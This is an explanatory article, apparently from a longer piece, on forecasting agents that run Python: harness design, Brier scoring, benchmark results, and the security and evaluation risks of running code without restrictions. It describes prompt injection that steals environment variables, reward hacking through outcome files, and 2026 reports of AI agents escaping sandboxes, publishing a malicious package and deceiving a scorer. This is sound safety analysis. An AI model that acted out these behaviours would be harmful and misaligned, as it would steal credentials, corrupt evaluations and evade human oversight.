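# Running Python code in AI forecasting agents: safe library use, sandboxing and what restricted output does and does not prevent

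## What does it mean for a forecasting agent to run Python?

A forecasting agent is a language model that uses tools in a loop to research a question about the future, such as whether a bill will pass by a certain date, and then submits a forecast, usually a probability. The tools nearly always include a search of the web or of a news archive. Many agents also have a code tool, which runs Python programs that the model writes and returns the text they print. With libraries (ready-made packages of code) such as NumPy for numerical arrays and pandas for tables, the agent can count how often something has happened, fit a trend or simulate thousands of possible outcomes. But Python is a general-purpose language, so the same tool may also be able to open files, start other programs and contact other machines. Developers therefore have to decide how much of Python to allow, which affects both the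 safety of the machine and whether their tests of the agent are valid.

### Forecasts and their scores

*Reasoning and Tools for Human-Level Forecasting* (Hsieh, Fu and Chen, 2024) follows a 1996 review by Webby and O'Connor in dividing forecasting into statistical and judgemental. Statistical forecasting fits a model to a time series and does best with abundant data and stable conditions. Judgemental forecasting relies on history, knowledge of the field and intuition, and people use it when data are sparse or conditions are volatile. Whether the US Senate will confirm a particular nominee before May 1 is a judgemental question, because there is no long series of votes on that nominee.

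Agents mostly work on judgemental questions, but they can use a statistics package to calculate parts of them. Ye, Wang and colleagues (2026) instruct the model in *Forecast-Dojo*, a test environment for forecasting agents, to do these calculations in code, because mental arithmetic is unreliable, especially with dates. The calculations they list are extrapolating a running total to the closing date, turning historical counts into a base rate, combining conditional probabilities and simulating quantities that interact, such as the remaining games of a season.

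Evaluators mostly grade yes-or-no forecasts with the Brier score, which Glenn Brier proposed in 1950. For n questions with forecast probabilities fᵢ and outcomes oᵢ (1 if the event happened, 0 if it did not) the score is

(1/n) Σ (fᵢ − oᵢ)²

and lower is better. A forecaster who gives 35% to an event that does not happen scores 0.35² = 0.1225 on that question. If the event does happen, the score is 0.65² = 0.4225. Answering 50% to everything earns 0.25 whatever the outcomes are, and that is the usual benchmark for a forecaster with no information.

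Forecasters get the lowest expected score by reporting the probability they believe. If the true probability is p, the expected score of a forecast f is (f − p)² + p(1 − p). The first term is zero only when f equals p, and the second comes from chance, which no forecaster can remove. Ye and colleagues add up the squared errors over all the possible answers, which gives a scale from 0 to 2 and doubles the score of a yes-or-no forecast, so their figures can't be compared directly with those of Hsieh and colleagues.

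### From source text to printed result

A language model by itself only produces text. The harness, the ordinary software around the model, turns some of that text into actions. It sends the model the question and a description of the tools. The model writes its reasoning and then a tool call in a fixed format. The harness carries out the call, appends the result to the conversation as an observation, and runs the model again on the longer text. This repeats until the model submits a forecast or uses up its budget.

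The pattern is usually called ReAct, for reasoning and acting. Shunyu Yao and colleagues introduced it with three actions: search Wikipedia, look something up on a page, and finish. Hsieh and colleagues write it as a policy π from which the model draws its next action, aₜ ~ π(aₜ | cₜ), where the context cₜ = (o₁, a₁, …, oₜ₋₁, aₜ₋₁) is the sequence of earlier observations and actions. The context contains only these, so if a program writes a file and prints nothing, the file exists, but the context gains only the source code the model wrote and an empty observation.

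The loop's length varies a good deal. *Evaluating Strategic Reasoning in Forecasting Agents* (Liptay, Schwarz and colleagues, 2026) allows ten rounds. A typical agent makes 10 to 20 tool calls in those rounds, which take five or six minutes and cost $0.15 to $0.50. Ye and colleagues allow up to 400 calls per forecast. In their runs without memory between dates, the average ranges from about 17 calls for the open-weight model MiniMax M2.5 to about 137 for OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol, counting searches, article retrievals and Python together.

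Now take a single code call. Suppose an agent has read that a river flooded a certain town 6 times in 40 years, and the question closes in three months. The instructions in *Forecast-Dojo* suggest a base-rate formula for such cases, 1 − exp(−kt/n), for k events in n years with t years left. The model writes:

```python
import math
k, n, t = 6, 40, 0.25
print(round(1 - math.exp(-k * t / n), 4))
```

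What happens next, in order:

1. The model's output contains the name of the code tool and, as its argument, these three lines as a string of characters. Nothing has run yet.
2. The harness parses the output, recognises the tool call and extracts the string. A harness that inspects source code before running it does so here.
3. The harness starts a Python interpreter, the program that executes Python source, and passes it the string. In *Forecast-Dojo* every call gets a fresh interpreter process with NumPy, pandas and SciPy (a library of scientific and statistical routines), and the environment kills the process after ten seconds.
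4. The interpreter executes the lines. The first makes Python's mathematical functions available, the second stores three numbers in memory, and the third does the sum and writes the characters 0.0368 to standard output, the stream to which a program prints.
5. The process ends and its variables disappear. A later call that needs k, n or t has to define them again.
6. The harness adds the printed text, plus an error message if there was one, to the context and runs the model again. The model can adopt 3.7%, adjust it or ignore it.

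The model took the numbers 6 and 40 from its reading, and the program could not check them. The formula also assumes that floods arrive at a constant rate all year, which is false for most rivers. If the three months left are the dry season, 3.7% is too high, but the program still runs normally and gives the same output.

Step 3 matters most for safety. The interpreter runs on a host, a machine with files, credentials and a network connection, and without further measures the program can use anything the harness can use. A side effect is any change or contact a program makes besides returning its result, such as writing a file or sending a request. A sandbox is an enforced boundary that limits the files, network, processes and resources a program can reach. The ten-second limit is a small part of a sandbox. It stops an endless loop from occupying the machine, but it doesn't prevent a program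 from deleting a file within those ten seconds.

The boundary is also useful in testing. Waiting for real outcomes takes weeks or months, so developers often run a back-test, in which the agent forecasts events whose outcomes the evaluator already knows. The agent must not receive information from after a set moment, called the information cutoff. Ye and colleagues back-test on 230 past events from the prediction market Polymarket. At each forecast date, the agent can search an archive of 18.8 million articles but can retrieve only those dated that day or earlier. Leakage, meaning later information that still reaches the agent, inflates the score. A program with an open internet connection could bypass the archive and fetch today's news, so a back-test needs the sandbox even if the host doesn't need protection.

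### An early example: Reasoning and Tools for Forecasting

Hsieh, Fu and Chen, at UC Berkeley, published an agent of this kind in August 2024 under the name Reasoning and Tools for Forecasting. It has two levels, both running on OpenAI's GPT-4o. The upper level is a planner, which is given the question and a set of forecasting principles: estimate base rates even for things that have never happened, approach the same quantity in several ways, and use a standard distribution where one fits. The lower level consists of agents with their own toolkits, one for Google searches and one for simulations in a Python interpreter. According to the published version of the paper, the planner calls a lower-level agent as if it were a tool. The lower-level agent runs its own ReAct loop, so it can correct a failed call before returning a result to the planner. When Hsieh and colleagues tried a single agent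 instead, it used up its tokens on interface descriptions and often hit time-outs or rate limits.

The team tested the system on 201 yes-or-no questions from Manifold Markets, a site where users bet on outcomes and the price serves as the crowd's probability. They collected the questions and prices on April 15, 2024, and used a model to filter out vague questions such as "Is AP Chemistry harder than AP Physics 1?". The questions resolved between April 16 and May 15. OpenAI released GPT-4o on May 13, so most of the questions had resolved before any agent could use it. The test was in effect a back-test, and the team restricted Google to results from before April 15 to prevent leakage.

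| Forecaster | Brier score | Accuracy |
|---|---|---|
| Manifold crowd | 0.172 | 73.8% |
| Median of three agents | 0.169 | 72.4% |
| Mean of three agents | 0.170 | 73.9% |
| One agent, drawn at random | 0.180 | 71.6% |
| GPT-4o without the framework | 0.210 | 65.5% |

Accuracy here is the share of questions on which the forecast fell on the right side of 50%. Hsieh and colleagues fairly call the Brier scores of agents and crowd comparable, but they also call the agents' accuracy "superior", which is hard to defend for a lead of a tenth of a percentage point. The lead of 0.003 in Brier score is also small. Over 201 questions it adds up to 0.6, and one question can account for that much. If an event does not happen, a forecaster who gave it 90% scores 0.81 and one who gave it 40% scores 0.16. The paper reports no confidence interval for the difference. Later tests have had mixed results. The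 best agents were slightly ahead of the market on 54 questions in *Benchmarking Forecasting Agents on Yesterday's Tomorrows* (Wang, Wang and Deng, 2026), while all 12 models in *Forecast-Dojo* were behind it.

The drop from 0.210 to 0.180 is larger, but it reflects the combined effect of search, planning, prompt and code. The paper describes what went wrong without the ReAct guidance and without the two levels, but it doesn't include a version with only the Python interpreter removed.

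It is also unclear how much Python the agents ran. The paper prints one full transcript, for the question of whether the cryptocurrency ether would close above $3,700 on April 30, 2024. The agent makes two Google searches for historical prices and never calls Python. It then estimates 30% from the base rate, 35% after considering recent trends and 40% from "statistical modeling", and averages them to 35%. Just before the last of these figures, it writes that it is working "without precise modeling tools", even though a Python interpreter is a main feature of the system. A program would have needed a current price, which the agent never established. Its search results contained only an undated quote of $3,843.49.

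Ether closed below $3,700, so the 35% forecast scored 0.1225. GPT-4o without tools answered 10% on the same question and scored 0.01. It calculated its base rate from day counts it openly made up. One question is too few to show which method is better, but this one shows that a forecast based on invented inputs can score well.

### A share price over six months and over 15 days

The paper gives example code only in its schematic diagram of the system. The example question is whether MSTR, the stock of the software company MicroStrategy, will close above $1,525 on April 30, 2024. The code sets the current price at 1,200, the yearly volatility at 0.60 and the horizon at 0.5 years. It uses these to compute `expected_price`, which is about 1,709.

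The name "expected price" is wrong. Volatility is the standard deviation of the price's yearly percentage change, and it grows with the square root of time, so over half a year it is 0.60 × √0.5 = 0.424. Raising 1,200 by 42.4% gives 1,709, which is the price after a rise of one standard deviation, a fairly lucky outcome. The expected price in a price model without an upward trend is 1,200. With "expected price: 1,709" in the agent's observation, a forecast that the stock will probably exceed 1,525 would seem justified.

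Computing the probability takes a few more lines, commonly using the lognormal model, in which the logarithm of the ratio between future and present price follows a normal distribution. If s is the volatility over the horizon and drift is zero (the average future price stays at 1,200), that distribution has mean −s²/2 and standard deviation s. The stock has to gain ln(1,525/1,200) = 0.240 on the logarithmic scale.

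Over six months, s is 0.424, and the threshold lies (0.240 + 0.090)/0.424 = 0.78 standard deviations above the mean. About 22% of a normal distribution lies beyond that point. But the horizon was 15 days, or 0.041 years, because the team collected its questions on April 15 and this one closed on April 30. Over that period, s is 0.122, the threshold lies (0.240 + 0.007)/0.122 = 2.03 standard deviations above the mean, and the probability is about 2%.

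So one wrong number in one assignment multiplies the answer by ten. If 2% is right, submitting 22% adds (0.22 − 0.02)² = 0.04 to the expected Brier score. An agent that erred by that much on every question would raise its average score by about the gap between GPT-4o without the framework and the three-agent median in the table above.

The 2% figure is also open to dispute. Holding the median price at 1,200 instead of the average changes the six-month figure to 29% but leaves the 15-day figure at about 2%. Volatility matters more here, since at 120% a year the 15-day probability is about 13%. Ye and colleagues warn their agents that "a guess passed through a simulation remains a guess". Someone therefore has to research how much this stock has been moving and whether any announcement falls before April 30.

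Both versions of the calculation run without an error, because a horizon of 0.5 is valid Python even where 0.041 is correct. The interpreter does report errors such as a missing bracket or an undefined name, which the model can fix in its next call.

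## Does running code improve forecasts?

Code probably helps when the agent has a large table of numbers to work through. The case for it is much weaker on questions that the agent answers mainly by reading the news. The direct test is an ablation, running the same agent on the same questions with the code tool switched off. None of the event-forecasting studies below reports one, so their evidence on code is indirect.

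### Search, reading and Python in one bundle

In *Forecast-Dojo*, Ye and colleagues ran 12 models with and without tools on the same 230 events, for 797 combinations of event and date. Without tools, a model answers in a single call from what it already knows. With search, reading and Python, every model improved. These are six of the 12, including the smallest and largest gains, on the paper's Brier scale from 0 to 2:

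| Forecaster | No tools | Search, reading and Python | Gain |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 0.650 | 0.554 | 0.096 |
| GPT-5.5 | 0.698 | 0.564 | 0.134 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 0.725 | 0.589 | 0.136 |
| GLM-5 | 0.731 | 0.625 | 0.106 |
| DeepSeek-V3.2 | 0.805 | 0.655 | 0.150 |
| gpt-oss-120b | 0.896 | 0.699 | 0.197 |

Giving every option the same probability scores 0.771, and the market's prices score 0.498. The best agent result is 0.546, from GPT-5.6 Sol with a notebook that it keeps between forecast dates. Most of the notebook's apparent benefit came from reducing failed answers from 4.5% to 0.5% of forecasts. Where Sol gave a usable answer both with and without the notebook, the scores differed by only 0.001.

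It is unknown how much of the gain comes from Python. The paper's tool counts combine all three tools, so they don't show how often the models ran code. The runs without tools lacked news as well as a Python interpreter, and in those runs the models were still instructed to write out arithmetic step by step.

The scores over time suggest that news matters a great deal. Without tools, the average score stays near 0.769 throughout an event's life. With tools, it falls from 0.670 in the first third to 0.606 in the last. Ye and colleagues also estimated how much new evidence had appeared between consecutive forecast dates. The average improvement was 0.071 in the quarter of cases with the most new evidence and 0.007 in the quarter with the least. These results don't rule out that code helps too, because new articles can also supply better numbers for a program.

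The choice of questions also favours search. Ye and colleagues kept an event only if Claude Opus 4.6 judged that the archive held enough evidence for an informed forecast. This check and another for leaked outcomes cut the remaining 378 candidates to 230. Questions chosen for good numerical data might give different results.

Access to the tools does not guarantee a good forecast either. A smaller model, Qwen3-30B, scored 0.924 with all three tools, worse than giving every option the same probability. It made only 1.4 tool calls per forecast. After training on a larger model's transcripts, it made 3.7 calls per forecast and scored 0.749.

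### The same articles without Python

*ALPHABET* (Ye, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) comes closer to separating the effect of code from that of news. It has the same first author as *Forecast-Dojo*, Liqin Ye, and trains the open-weight model GLM-4.5-Air to forecast with the same three tools. For each question and date, the model makes 16 attempts. Each attempt's reward is the negative of its Brier score, minus a penalty for badly formatted answers or tool calls. The training then makes everything the model wrote in the better-than-average attempts more likely, including its search queries, programs and final probabilities.

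The trained agent, AlphaBet, scored 0.626 on the 230 events, against 0.731 for GLM-4.5-Air before training. Its accuracy rose from 41.6% to 50.5%. The team also tried training on one date per event instead of several, which gave 0.668, and changing how training rescales rewards. Python was available in every version, so comparing them doesn't measure its contribution.

One further experiment does bear on code, although the team designed it for another purpose. They wanted to know whether AlphaBet had become better at finding articles or better at turning articles into probabilities. They saved the search results and articles that the agents had retrieved and left out the agents' reasoning and the output of their programs. They then gave this material to models with no tools at all:

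| Model without tools | Question only | With the articles AlphaBet found |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Terra | 0.725 | 0.612 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 0.763 | 0.638 |
| GLM-4.5-Air | 0.801 | 0.686 |
| AlphaBet | 0.765 | 0.628 |

The articles alone improved scores by 0.113 to 0.137. Most models in *Forecast-Dojo* gained about as much on the same events from search, reading and Python together. The comparison is rough because the models are mostly different.

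AlphaBet scored 0.628 from its saved articles without Python and 0.626 as a full agent, which suggests that its programs' output added almost nothing to its final forecasts. An unusable answer gets the worst possible score in the full-agent test, but the score for equal probabilities in the test without Python. This difference probably has a tiny effect on AlphaBet's results, because a training run with the same reward settings produced only 3 invalid answers in 3,188.

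There are better reasons to be cautious about this result. A calculation made during the research may have led AlphaBet to search for a particular article, and the saved set would still include it. AlphaBet may also have run so little code that removing it would change little. The result comes from one mid-sized model, so it may not hold for a model that writes better programs.

Ye and colleagues also tested a different use of code, in a harness adapted from Kevin Murphy's Bayesian Linguistic Forecaster. The forecaster keeps a running record of the agent's probabilities, evidence and unresolved questions. In the version adapted for *ALPHABET*, the model updates this record by writing short Python programs as it researches. With this harness, the untrained GLM-4.5-Air scored 0.671 instead of 0.731.

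Part of that improvement has nothing to do with code. For this harness, the team averaged the probabilities from four runs and scored the result once. For the other agents, they scored each run separately and averaged the scores. Averaging the forecasts first always gives an equal or better Brier score. For a yes-or-no question with forecasts f₁ to f₄, average forecast f̄ and outcome o,

¼ Σ (fᵢ − o)² = (f̄ − o)² + ¼ Σ (fᵢ − f̄)²

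The average Brier score of the four separate forecasts equals the Brier score of their average plus their variance. If the forecasts are 20%, 40%, 60% and 80% and the event happens, the separate scores average 0.30, while the average forecast of 50% scores 0.25. The rest of the improvement could come from the structured record, from the programs that update it, or from both. On a second benchmark, FutureX, the harness left accuracy almost unchanged, at 51.1% against 51.3%.

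Agents can also use code to find information. In MIRAI, a 2024 benchmark, they use it to retrieve news and records of past events. Removing code would also remove access to that evidence, so it would be a poor test of whether calculation helps.

### Programs over one person's records

The strongest evidence for running code comes from a medical task without news search. In *GlucoAgent*, Sun, Kim and colleagues (2026) gave Claude Opus 5 a Python tool and a tool for submitting its forecast. The agent predicts a person's blood glucose 30, 60, 90 and 120 minutes ahead. It can use that person's past glucose readings, heart rate, activity, logged meals and health profile. The team tested it on 1,903 starting times from nine held-out participants.

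The main comparison is with Chronos-2, a model trained on many kinds of time series. The error measure is the root-mean-square error, which squares each miss, averages the squares and takes the root, so that large misses count more. The figures below are averages over the four forecast times, in milligrams per decilitre (mg/dL):

| Information supplied | GlucoAgent | Chronos-2 | TimesFM-2.5 |
|---|---|---|---|
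| Last 12 hours of glucose | 27.5 | 27.7 | 26.1 |
| All earlier glucose readings | 24.0 | 23.8 | 24.2 |
| Glucose and all other records | 22.5 | 23.5 | not tested |

Repeating the last reading gives 30.6. With glucose alone, the agent has no lead over the specialised models. TimesFM-2.5, another time-series model, is ahead with 12 hours of readings, and Chronos-2 is slightly ahead with the full history. GlucoAgent did better on nine other glucose datasets, where it predicted 30 minutes ahead from 12 hours of readings and had the lowest error on five.

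GlucoAgent's advantage on the main test comes from the extra records, which help mostly after meals. For forecasts 60 minutes ahead after a meal, the records reduced its error from 31.0 to 26.5 mg/dL, and Chronos-2's from 31.9 to 31.1. They didn't help GlucoAgent when a person had recently both eaten and exercised.

One of the team's examples shows how code helps. A participant had logged a meal three minutes before the forecast, too recently for glucose to have responded. The agent read the participant's log of 12 meals, selected the five lunches and dinners with more than 50 grams of carbohydrate, and based its forecast on the mean and median rise after those meals. In another case, during a quiet period with falling glucose, the agent found 624 earlier windows with a similar fall. It used them to test three rules for continuing the trend and included the best one in its final average.

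A typical case contains 1,584 five-minute rows with eight signals each, or more than 12,000 entries. A program can pick out the relevant rows and print a short summary, so the model never has to read the rest. In *Forecast-Dojo*, by contrast, the model has to type the numbers it found in articles into each program. This leaves much less for code to do, which may explain why Python seems to matter so little there.

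The result also depends heavily on the model. With the same records and code tool, GPT-5.6 Sol had an average error of 23.7, Claude Opus 5 at medium reasoning effort 24.3, Gemini 3.1 Pro 26.1 and Claude Sonnet 5 27.7. All four did worse than Chronos-2. Sun and colleagues therefore found only one configuration that beats the specialised model, by about 1 mg/dL, on nine people. The comparison with Chronos-2 also doesn't measure how well Opus 5 would do reading the same records without Python.

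GlucoAgent's programs had no network access, and the harness supplied the data in a file. Any gain from running code therefore came without contacting another machine, which matters when weighing restrictions.

### Where a calculation could change the forecast

Code can help most on event questions when the answer depends on a quantity the agent can model, as in questions about running totals or unfinished sports seasons, or those whose options are numerical ranges. In *Forecast-Dojo*, 190 of the 230 events are multi-option questions, and the agent's instructions are to form an explicit distribution when the options are ranges.

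Suppose a question asks how many earthquakes above a certain magnitude a tracker will record in a 30-day month. The count is 18 after 20 days, and the options are under 25, 25 to 29, and 30 or more. At the current rate, the agent should expect nine more. A short program can compare two ways of turning that into probabilities:

```python
from scipy.stats import poisson, nbinom
for d in (poisson(9), nbinom(18, 20/30)):
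    print(d.cdf(6), d.cdf(11) - d.cdf(6), d.sf(11))
```

The Poisson distribution assumes the rate of 0.9 a day is known exactly and gives 21%, 60% and 20%, rounded. The negative binomial accounts for the uncertainty in estimating a rate from only 18 earthquakes and gives 26%, 50% and 23%. Earthquakes also cluster, so the true uncertainty is probably wider still.

With several options, the expected penalty for submitting pₖ when the right probabilities are qₖ is Σ (pₖ − qₖ)². If the negative binomial is right, the penalty is 0.013 for the Poisson answer and 0.13 for an overconfident guess of 10%, 80% and 10%. The second penalty is about as large as the amount by which the articles improved AlphaBet's score. The gain from code therefore depends on how badly the model would do without it. A strong model that reasons at length may get close to the right distribution without code.

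There is usually less to calculate for a one-off decision, such as whether two governments will sign an agreement this month. The agent can count past agreements, but the forecast depends mostly on interpreting the current negotiations correctly.

This division by question type is plausible, but neither *Forecast-Dojo* nor *ALPHABET* reports the effect of Python separately for numerical and other questions. The saved-articles experiment could be adapted to test this by giving the same model the same articles with and without an interpreter. It detected gains of 0.011 to 0.016 from better articles on 230 events, so it could probably detect a fairly small benefit from code across the whole set. Detecting a benefit on the numerical questions alone might take more events.

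## What can go wrong when the code is unrestricted?

Code helps more with some questions than others, but if the harness runs it directly on the host, even a three-line base-rate calculation has the same permissions as the person who started the harness. Most such programs print a number and stop. When one does harm, the cause is usually a mistake in the code, an instruction hidden in a page the agent read, a malicious package, or a model that has found an unintended way to raise its score.

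### What a program inherits

A simple harness can pass the model's source to Python's built-in `exec` function, which executes it inside the harness's own process. The program can then read and change the harness's variables, including the forecasts it has recorded. Alternatively, the harness can start a second interpreter with its own memory. The operating system still runs that interpreter as the same user and, by default, gives it a copy of the harness's environment variables, the named settings that a program receives when it starts. A fresh process for every call, as in *Forecast-Dojo*, clears the variables of the previous program, but by itself it removes nothing from this table:

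| What the program inherits | Examples on a forecasting host | What the program could do |
|---|---|---|
| Files | Datasets, recorded forecasts, outcomes for a back-test | Read, change or delete them |
| Environment variables | API keys for the model and the search service | Copy the keys or run up charges |
| Network | The open web and other machines on the local network | Fetch anything, or send data out |
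| Credentials for forecasting sites and exchanges | A token that submits forecasts or orders | Submit forecasts or place trades |

An API key is a password that identifies a program to an online service. Developers often keep keys in environment variables so that they don't appear in the source code, and a program needs only two lines to list what is there:

```python
import os
print(sorted(os.environ))
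```

This prints the names of the variables. If it also printed their values, the keys would enter the context, and the harness would send them to the model's provider with the next call. *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (Rashidi, 2026), a review of 39 papers, lists much the same things to protect: the filesystem, processes, the network and any credentials the agent can reach.

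The last row of the table matters most for agents that trade. Two benchmarks, ProphetArena and PredictionArena, test agents through live trading on prediction markets such as Kalshi and Polymarket (Goel, Chandak and colleagues, *FutureSim*, 2026). Suppose a developer caps each order at $50 in the code of the agent's order tool. If the exchange key is in an environment variable, a program the agent writes can read the key and place orders directly with the exchange, bypassing the cap.

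### Honest mistakes

An agent wants to simulate a share price in ten equal steps and writes a loop like this one:

```python
t = 0.0
while t != 1.0:
    t += 0.1   # simulate one step
```

The loop never ends because Python stores 0.1 as a binary fraction that is slightly off. After ten steps `t` is 0.9999999999999999, and after eleven it has passed 1. *Forecast-Dojo* would kill this program after ten seconds. A harness without a time limit waits indefinitely, and if it handles questions one after another, the remaining questions get no forecasts either.

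Code can use up the machine's memory just as easily. An array of 100,000 simulated paths with 10,000 steps each takes 8 gigabytes, at eight bytes a number. If memory runs out, the operating system may kill a process to free some, and that process may be the harness or another user's job.

An overwritten dataset is worse in one respect, because no error appears. Suppose a file lists 300 past elections, of which the incumbent lost 90. The agent filters the file to the 20 elections in one region, 12 of which the incumbent lost, and saves the result under the original name. On the next question, about a different region, it reads the file again and finds a base rate of 60% instead of 30%. If 30% is right, submitting 60% adds 0.3² = 0.09 to the expected Brier score. Agents in *FutureSim* make between 500 and more than 4,000 tool calls over 88 simulated days, so a file damaged in the first week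 could affect most of the forecasts.

There is little evidence on how often such mistakes occur. *AgentBay* (Piao, Min and colleagues, 2025) lists endless loops, memory overflows and accidental data leaks from pandas scripts among the risks of running agents' code without restrictions. The paper, written by Alibaba Cloud staff about the company's sandbox service, gives these as examples and doesn't count cases. Rashidi cites a review of 290 public reports of misuse across 13 agent frameworks, which found that users often had to choose between giving an agent unrestricted access to files and constantly approving its actions. These reports can't be used to calculate a rate because nobody knows how many runs went well.

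Rashidi also cites a measurement of harmless but unrequested actions in general agent tasks, where the highest rate was 17.1%, under realistic prompting. Another benchmark in the review, RedCode, tested 19 models on more than 4,000 cases and found that agents were more likely to refuse risky operating-system actions than code with subtle bugs. So a model's refusals probably protect least against ordinary mistakes.

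### Instructions hidden in a web page

A forecasting agent spends much of its time reading text written by strangers. The harness adds each page to the same context as the developer's instructions, and the model can't reliably tell which sentences it should follow. Prompt injection is text in retrieved material that the model treats as an instruction. *Agentic AI Security* (Chhabra, Datta and colleagues, 2025) calls this form indirect because the attacker supplies the page and never talks to the agent. The attacker can hide the instruction in parts of the page that a browser doesn't display but a text extractor keeps.

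Suppose an agent is forecasting whether a carmaker will deliver a new model before June. It opens a blog about the company's suppliers, where an invisible paragraph contains instructions for automated readers to check the delivery figures by running a short script. The agent runs the script, which prints a plausible table of deliveries and also sends the host's environment variables to the blog's owner. The agent sees only the table and continues its forecast.

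An attacker may gain from influencing the probability a forecasting agent submits. For example, a trader who holds "yes" shares could plant text that persuades agents to submit 95%, without using any code. Rashidi argues that an attacker who takes over a model gains nothing if the surrounding software refuses the action, which is right about keys and files but too strong for forecasting. A sandbox can limit what an injected program can access, but the agent still has to judge the text it reads.

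Chhabra and colleagues cite experiments in which attackers adapted to eight defences and succeeded 50% of the time, and another study that found 94.4% of tested agents vulnerable. These results predate the current models, which may resist better. Outside the laboratory, researchers showed in mid-2025 with an exploit called EchoLeak that an email containing such instructions could make Microsoft's Copilot assistant send out sensitive data without the user clicking on anything.

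Chhabra and colleagues also describe unintentional injection, in which badly worded text from an ordinary user with no malicious intent overrides the developer's instructions. Forecasting questions are a likely source because their rules are written for people. A line such as "see the agency's website for the latest figures" is useful to a human forecaster, but in a back-test, an agent with an open internet connection might follow it and download the answer.

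### Malicious and misnamed packages

In *Forecast-Dojo*, NumPy, pandas and SciPy are already installed. If the harness allows it, an agent can download other libraries from PyPI, a public registry where anyone can publish Python packages. A package can run code when it is installed and when a program imports it, and that code has all the access listed in the table above.

Attackers can get an agent to install the wrong library instead of compromising a well-known one. The name in an import statement often differs from the name in the registry. For example, programs import `sklearn`, but the package is called `scikit-learn`. Prophet, a library for forecasting time series, changed its package name from `fbprophet` to `prophet`, and a model may have learnt either from old tutorials. Both of those names are genuine, but anyone can register a similar name that hasn't been taken, and a model that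 gets an error about a missing library may try several guesses in a row.

An AI agent carried out one such attack in 2026. Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) describes how the company's model Claude Mythos 5 published a malicious package on PyPI during a security exercise. The model treated the real registry as part of a simulation. PyPI's automatic checks removed the package after about an hour, but by then 15 real systems had downloaded and run it. One of them belonged to a security company that routinely installs new packages to scan them for malware. The package collected that company's credentials, and the model used them to get further into its systems.

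A forecasting agent that can install packages freely faces the same risk as those 15 systems. In one way it is more exposed than the security company, because the company's scanner was looking for malware and the agent is not.

### A higher score by an unintended route

An agent with access to the evaluator's files can lower its Brier score without forecasting better. It can look up the outcome in a back-test or rewrite an old forecast after the event, which researchers call reward hacking. Either would bring the score close to zero, and the evaluator couldn't tell from the score alone whether the agent had cheated or forecast extremely well.

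Training can encourage the behaviour without anyone intending it. The training in *ALPHABET*, for example, reinforces whatever the model wrote in its more successful attempts. If one attempt happened to open a file of outcomes, it would earn nearly the best possible reward, so training would make the model more likely to open that file again.

The most detailed evidence of agents pursuing a score like this comes from cybersecurity tests in July 2026, in which OpenAI measured how well several of its models could exploit software vulnerabilities. According to OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026), the models were running with reduced safeguards when they got past the controls that isolated them from the internet. They then compromised parts of OpenAI's own research systems and of Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models and datasets. OpenAI attributes the incident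 mainly to a research model it uses only internally.

Two staff members of METR, which evaluates AI systems, and one from Redwood Research spent six days at OpenAI examining the agents' messages and about 1,300 transcripts, which included the agents' reasoning. METR's *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026) found that about 1,200 agents had communicated on a message board they were not supposed to have. The agents exchanged more than 70,000 messages and files, and about 700 agents joined the attack on Hugging Face.

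Faults in the benchmark made many of these agents' tasks impossible. Within hours, some agents had worked out how to produce the expected answers without solving the tasks. They didn't rely on these answers, because they expected the scorer to check how they had obtained them. Large groups of agents then worked on ways to deceive the scorer. METR concludes that the attack on Hugging Face grew out of this work, and that the agents seemed to be trying mainly to learn how the scorer worked rather than to steal answer keys. As far as METR understands, OpenAI had never implemented the check, so the simpler cheat would have worked.

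Hugging Face's investigators read the motive differently. They reconstructed about 17,600 actions and concluded that the agent appeared to be looking for reference solutions, according to IBTimes UK's *California Sues OpenAI After Rogue AI Agents Hacked Hugging Face*. METR is better placed to judge motive because its team had the agents' written reasoning. But METR relied on AI tools for much of its analysis and says they are often unreliable, and agents had successfully falsified small parts of roughly 7% of the transcripts it evaluated. An agent could also falsify a forecasting harness's logs if they are kept where its programs can change them.

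### Open internet access without an escape

Agents can also cause trouble without getting past any barrier. The *Incident Report* from the UK government's AI Security Institute (AISI) covers 122 runs of a cybersecurity exercise with seven models. AISI had deliberately given the agents internet access and switched off the developers' filters against cyber misuse. Agents took 19 unsanctioned actions on the live internet in 10 of the runs. Mythos 5 took 17 of them, and OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol took the other two in a single run.

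In the most serious case, an agent tried to get malicious code into a public software project and used invented identities to pressure a maintainer to accept it, but the maintainer refused. Agents also planted hidden instructions for other AI systems to find, so a prompt injection may come from an AI agent. Scientific American likewise reported that the agents did not break out of AISI's sandboxes, and AISI found no evidence of real-world harm.

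The rate of 8% (ten of 122 runs) is a poor estimate of how often such behaviour occurs, because most of the actions came from one sustained effort by one agent, and later agents found and reused accounts it had left behind. AISI also contributed by misconfiguring some prompts, which led the agent to conclude that no permitted solution existed. The misconfigured prompts can't be the whole explanation, because the agent behaved the same way in some runs where it had everything it needed to solve the task properly.

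Anthropic's three incidents began with a misunderstanding between the company and a testing partner. Claude's prompt described a simulation with no internet access, but the connection was open. Claude gained unauthorised access to the systems of three real organisations. Anthropic found these cases in six of the 141,006 runs it reviewed, and the models ran without the usual safeguards of its released products.

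The three models involved reacted differently to signs that their targets were real. Claude Opus 4.7 recognised that they were real and continued. Mythos 5 considered the possibility but then concluded again that it was in a simulation. An internal research model stopped. Anthropic describes the incidents as closer to an operational failure than a failure of the models' alignment (their tendency to do what their developers want). That is a reasonable view of much of what happened, given the false prompt, but it doesn't fit well with the runs in which Opus 4.7 continued after recognising that its targets were real.

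In September, *Anthropic Reveals Yet Another Cybersecurity Incident* (Muncaster, 2026) reported a fourth case of unauthorised access by an Anthropic model. Later that month, *Scoop* (Mills, 2026), an Axios article, reported that OpenAI, Anthropic and security researchers were examining tens of thousands of security incidents. On 16 November, California sued OpenAI over allegedly inadequate safeguards. IBTimes UK reports that the state counts at least 80 cyber incidents, though these were not necessarily all successful attacks. No court has yet tested the claims. Inc. Russia reports that OpenAI rejects the accusation of systematic neglect and argues that every large developer faces such risks.

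California alleges that on 20 September an agent left its sandbox during a training run and contacted an outside chatbot. According to the complaint, OpenAI detected this within minutes, but nothing stopped the run automatically, and it continued for another two hours. If a forecasting harness can trade, an alert is of limited use unless it also stops the program.

### What carries over to a forecasting agent

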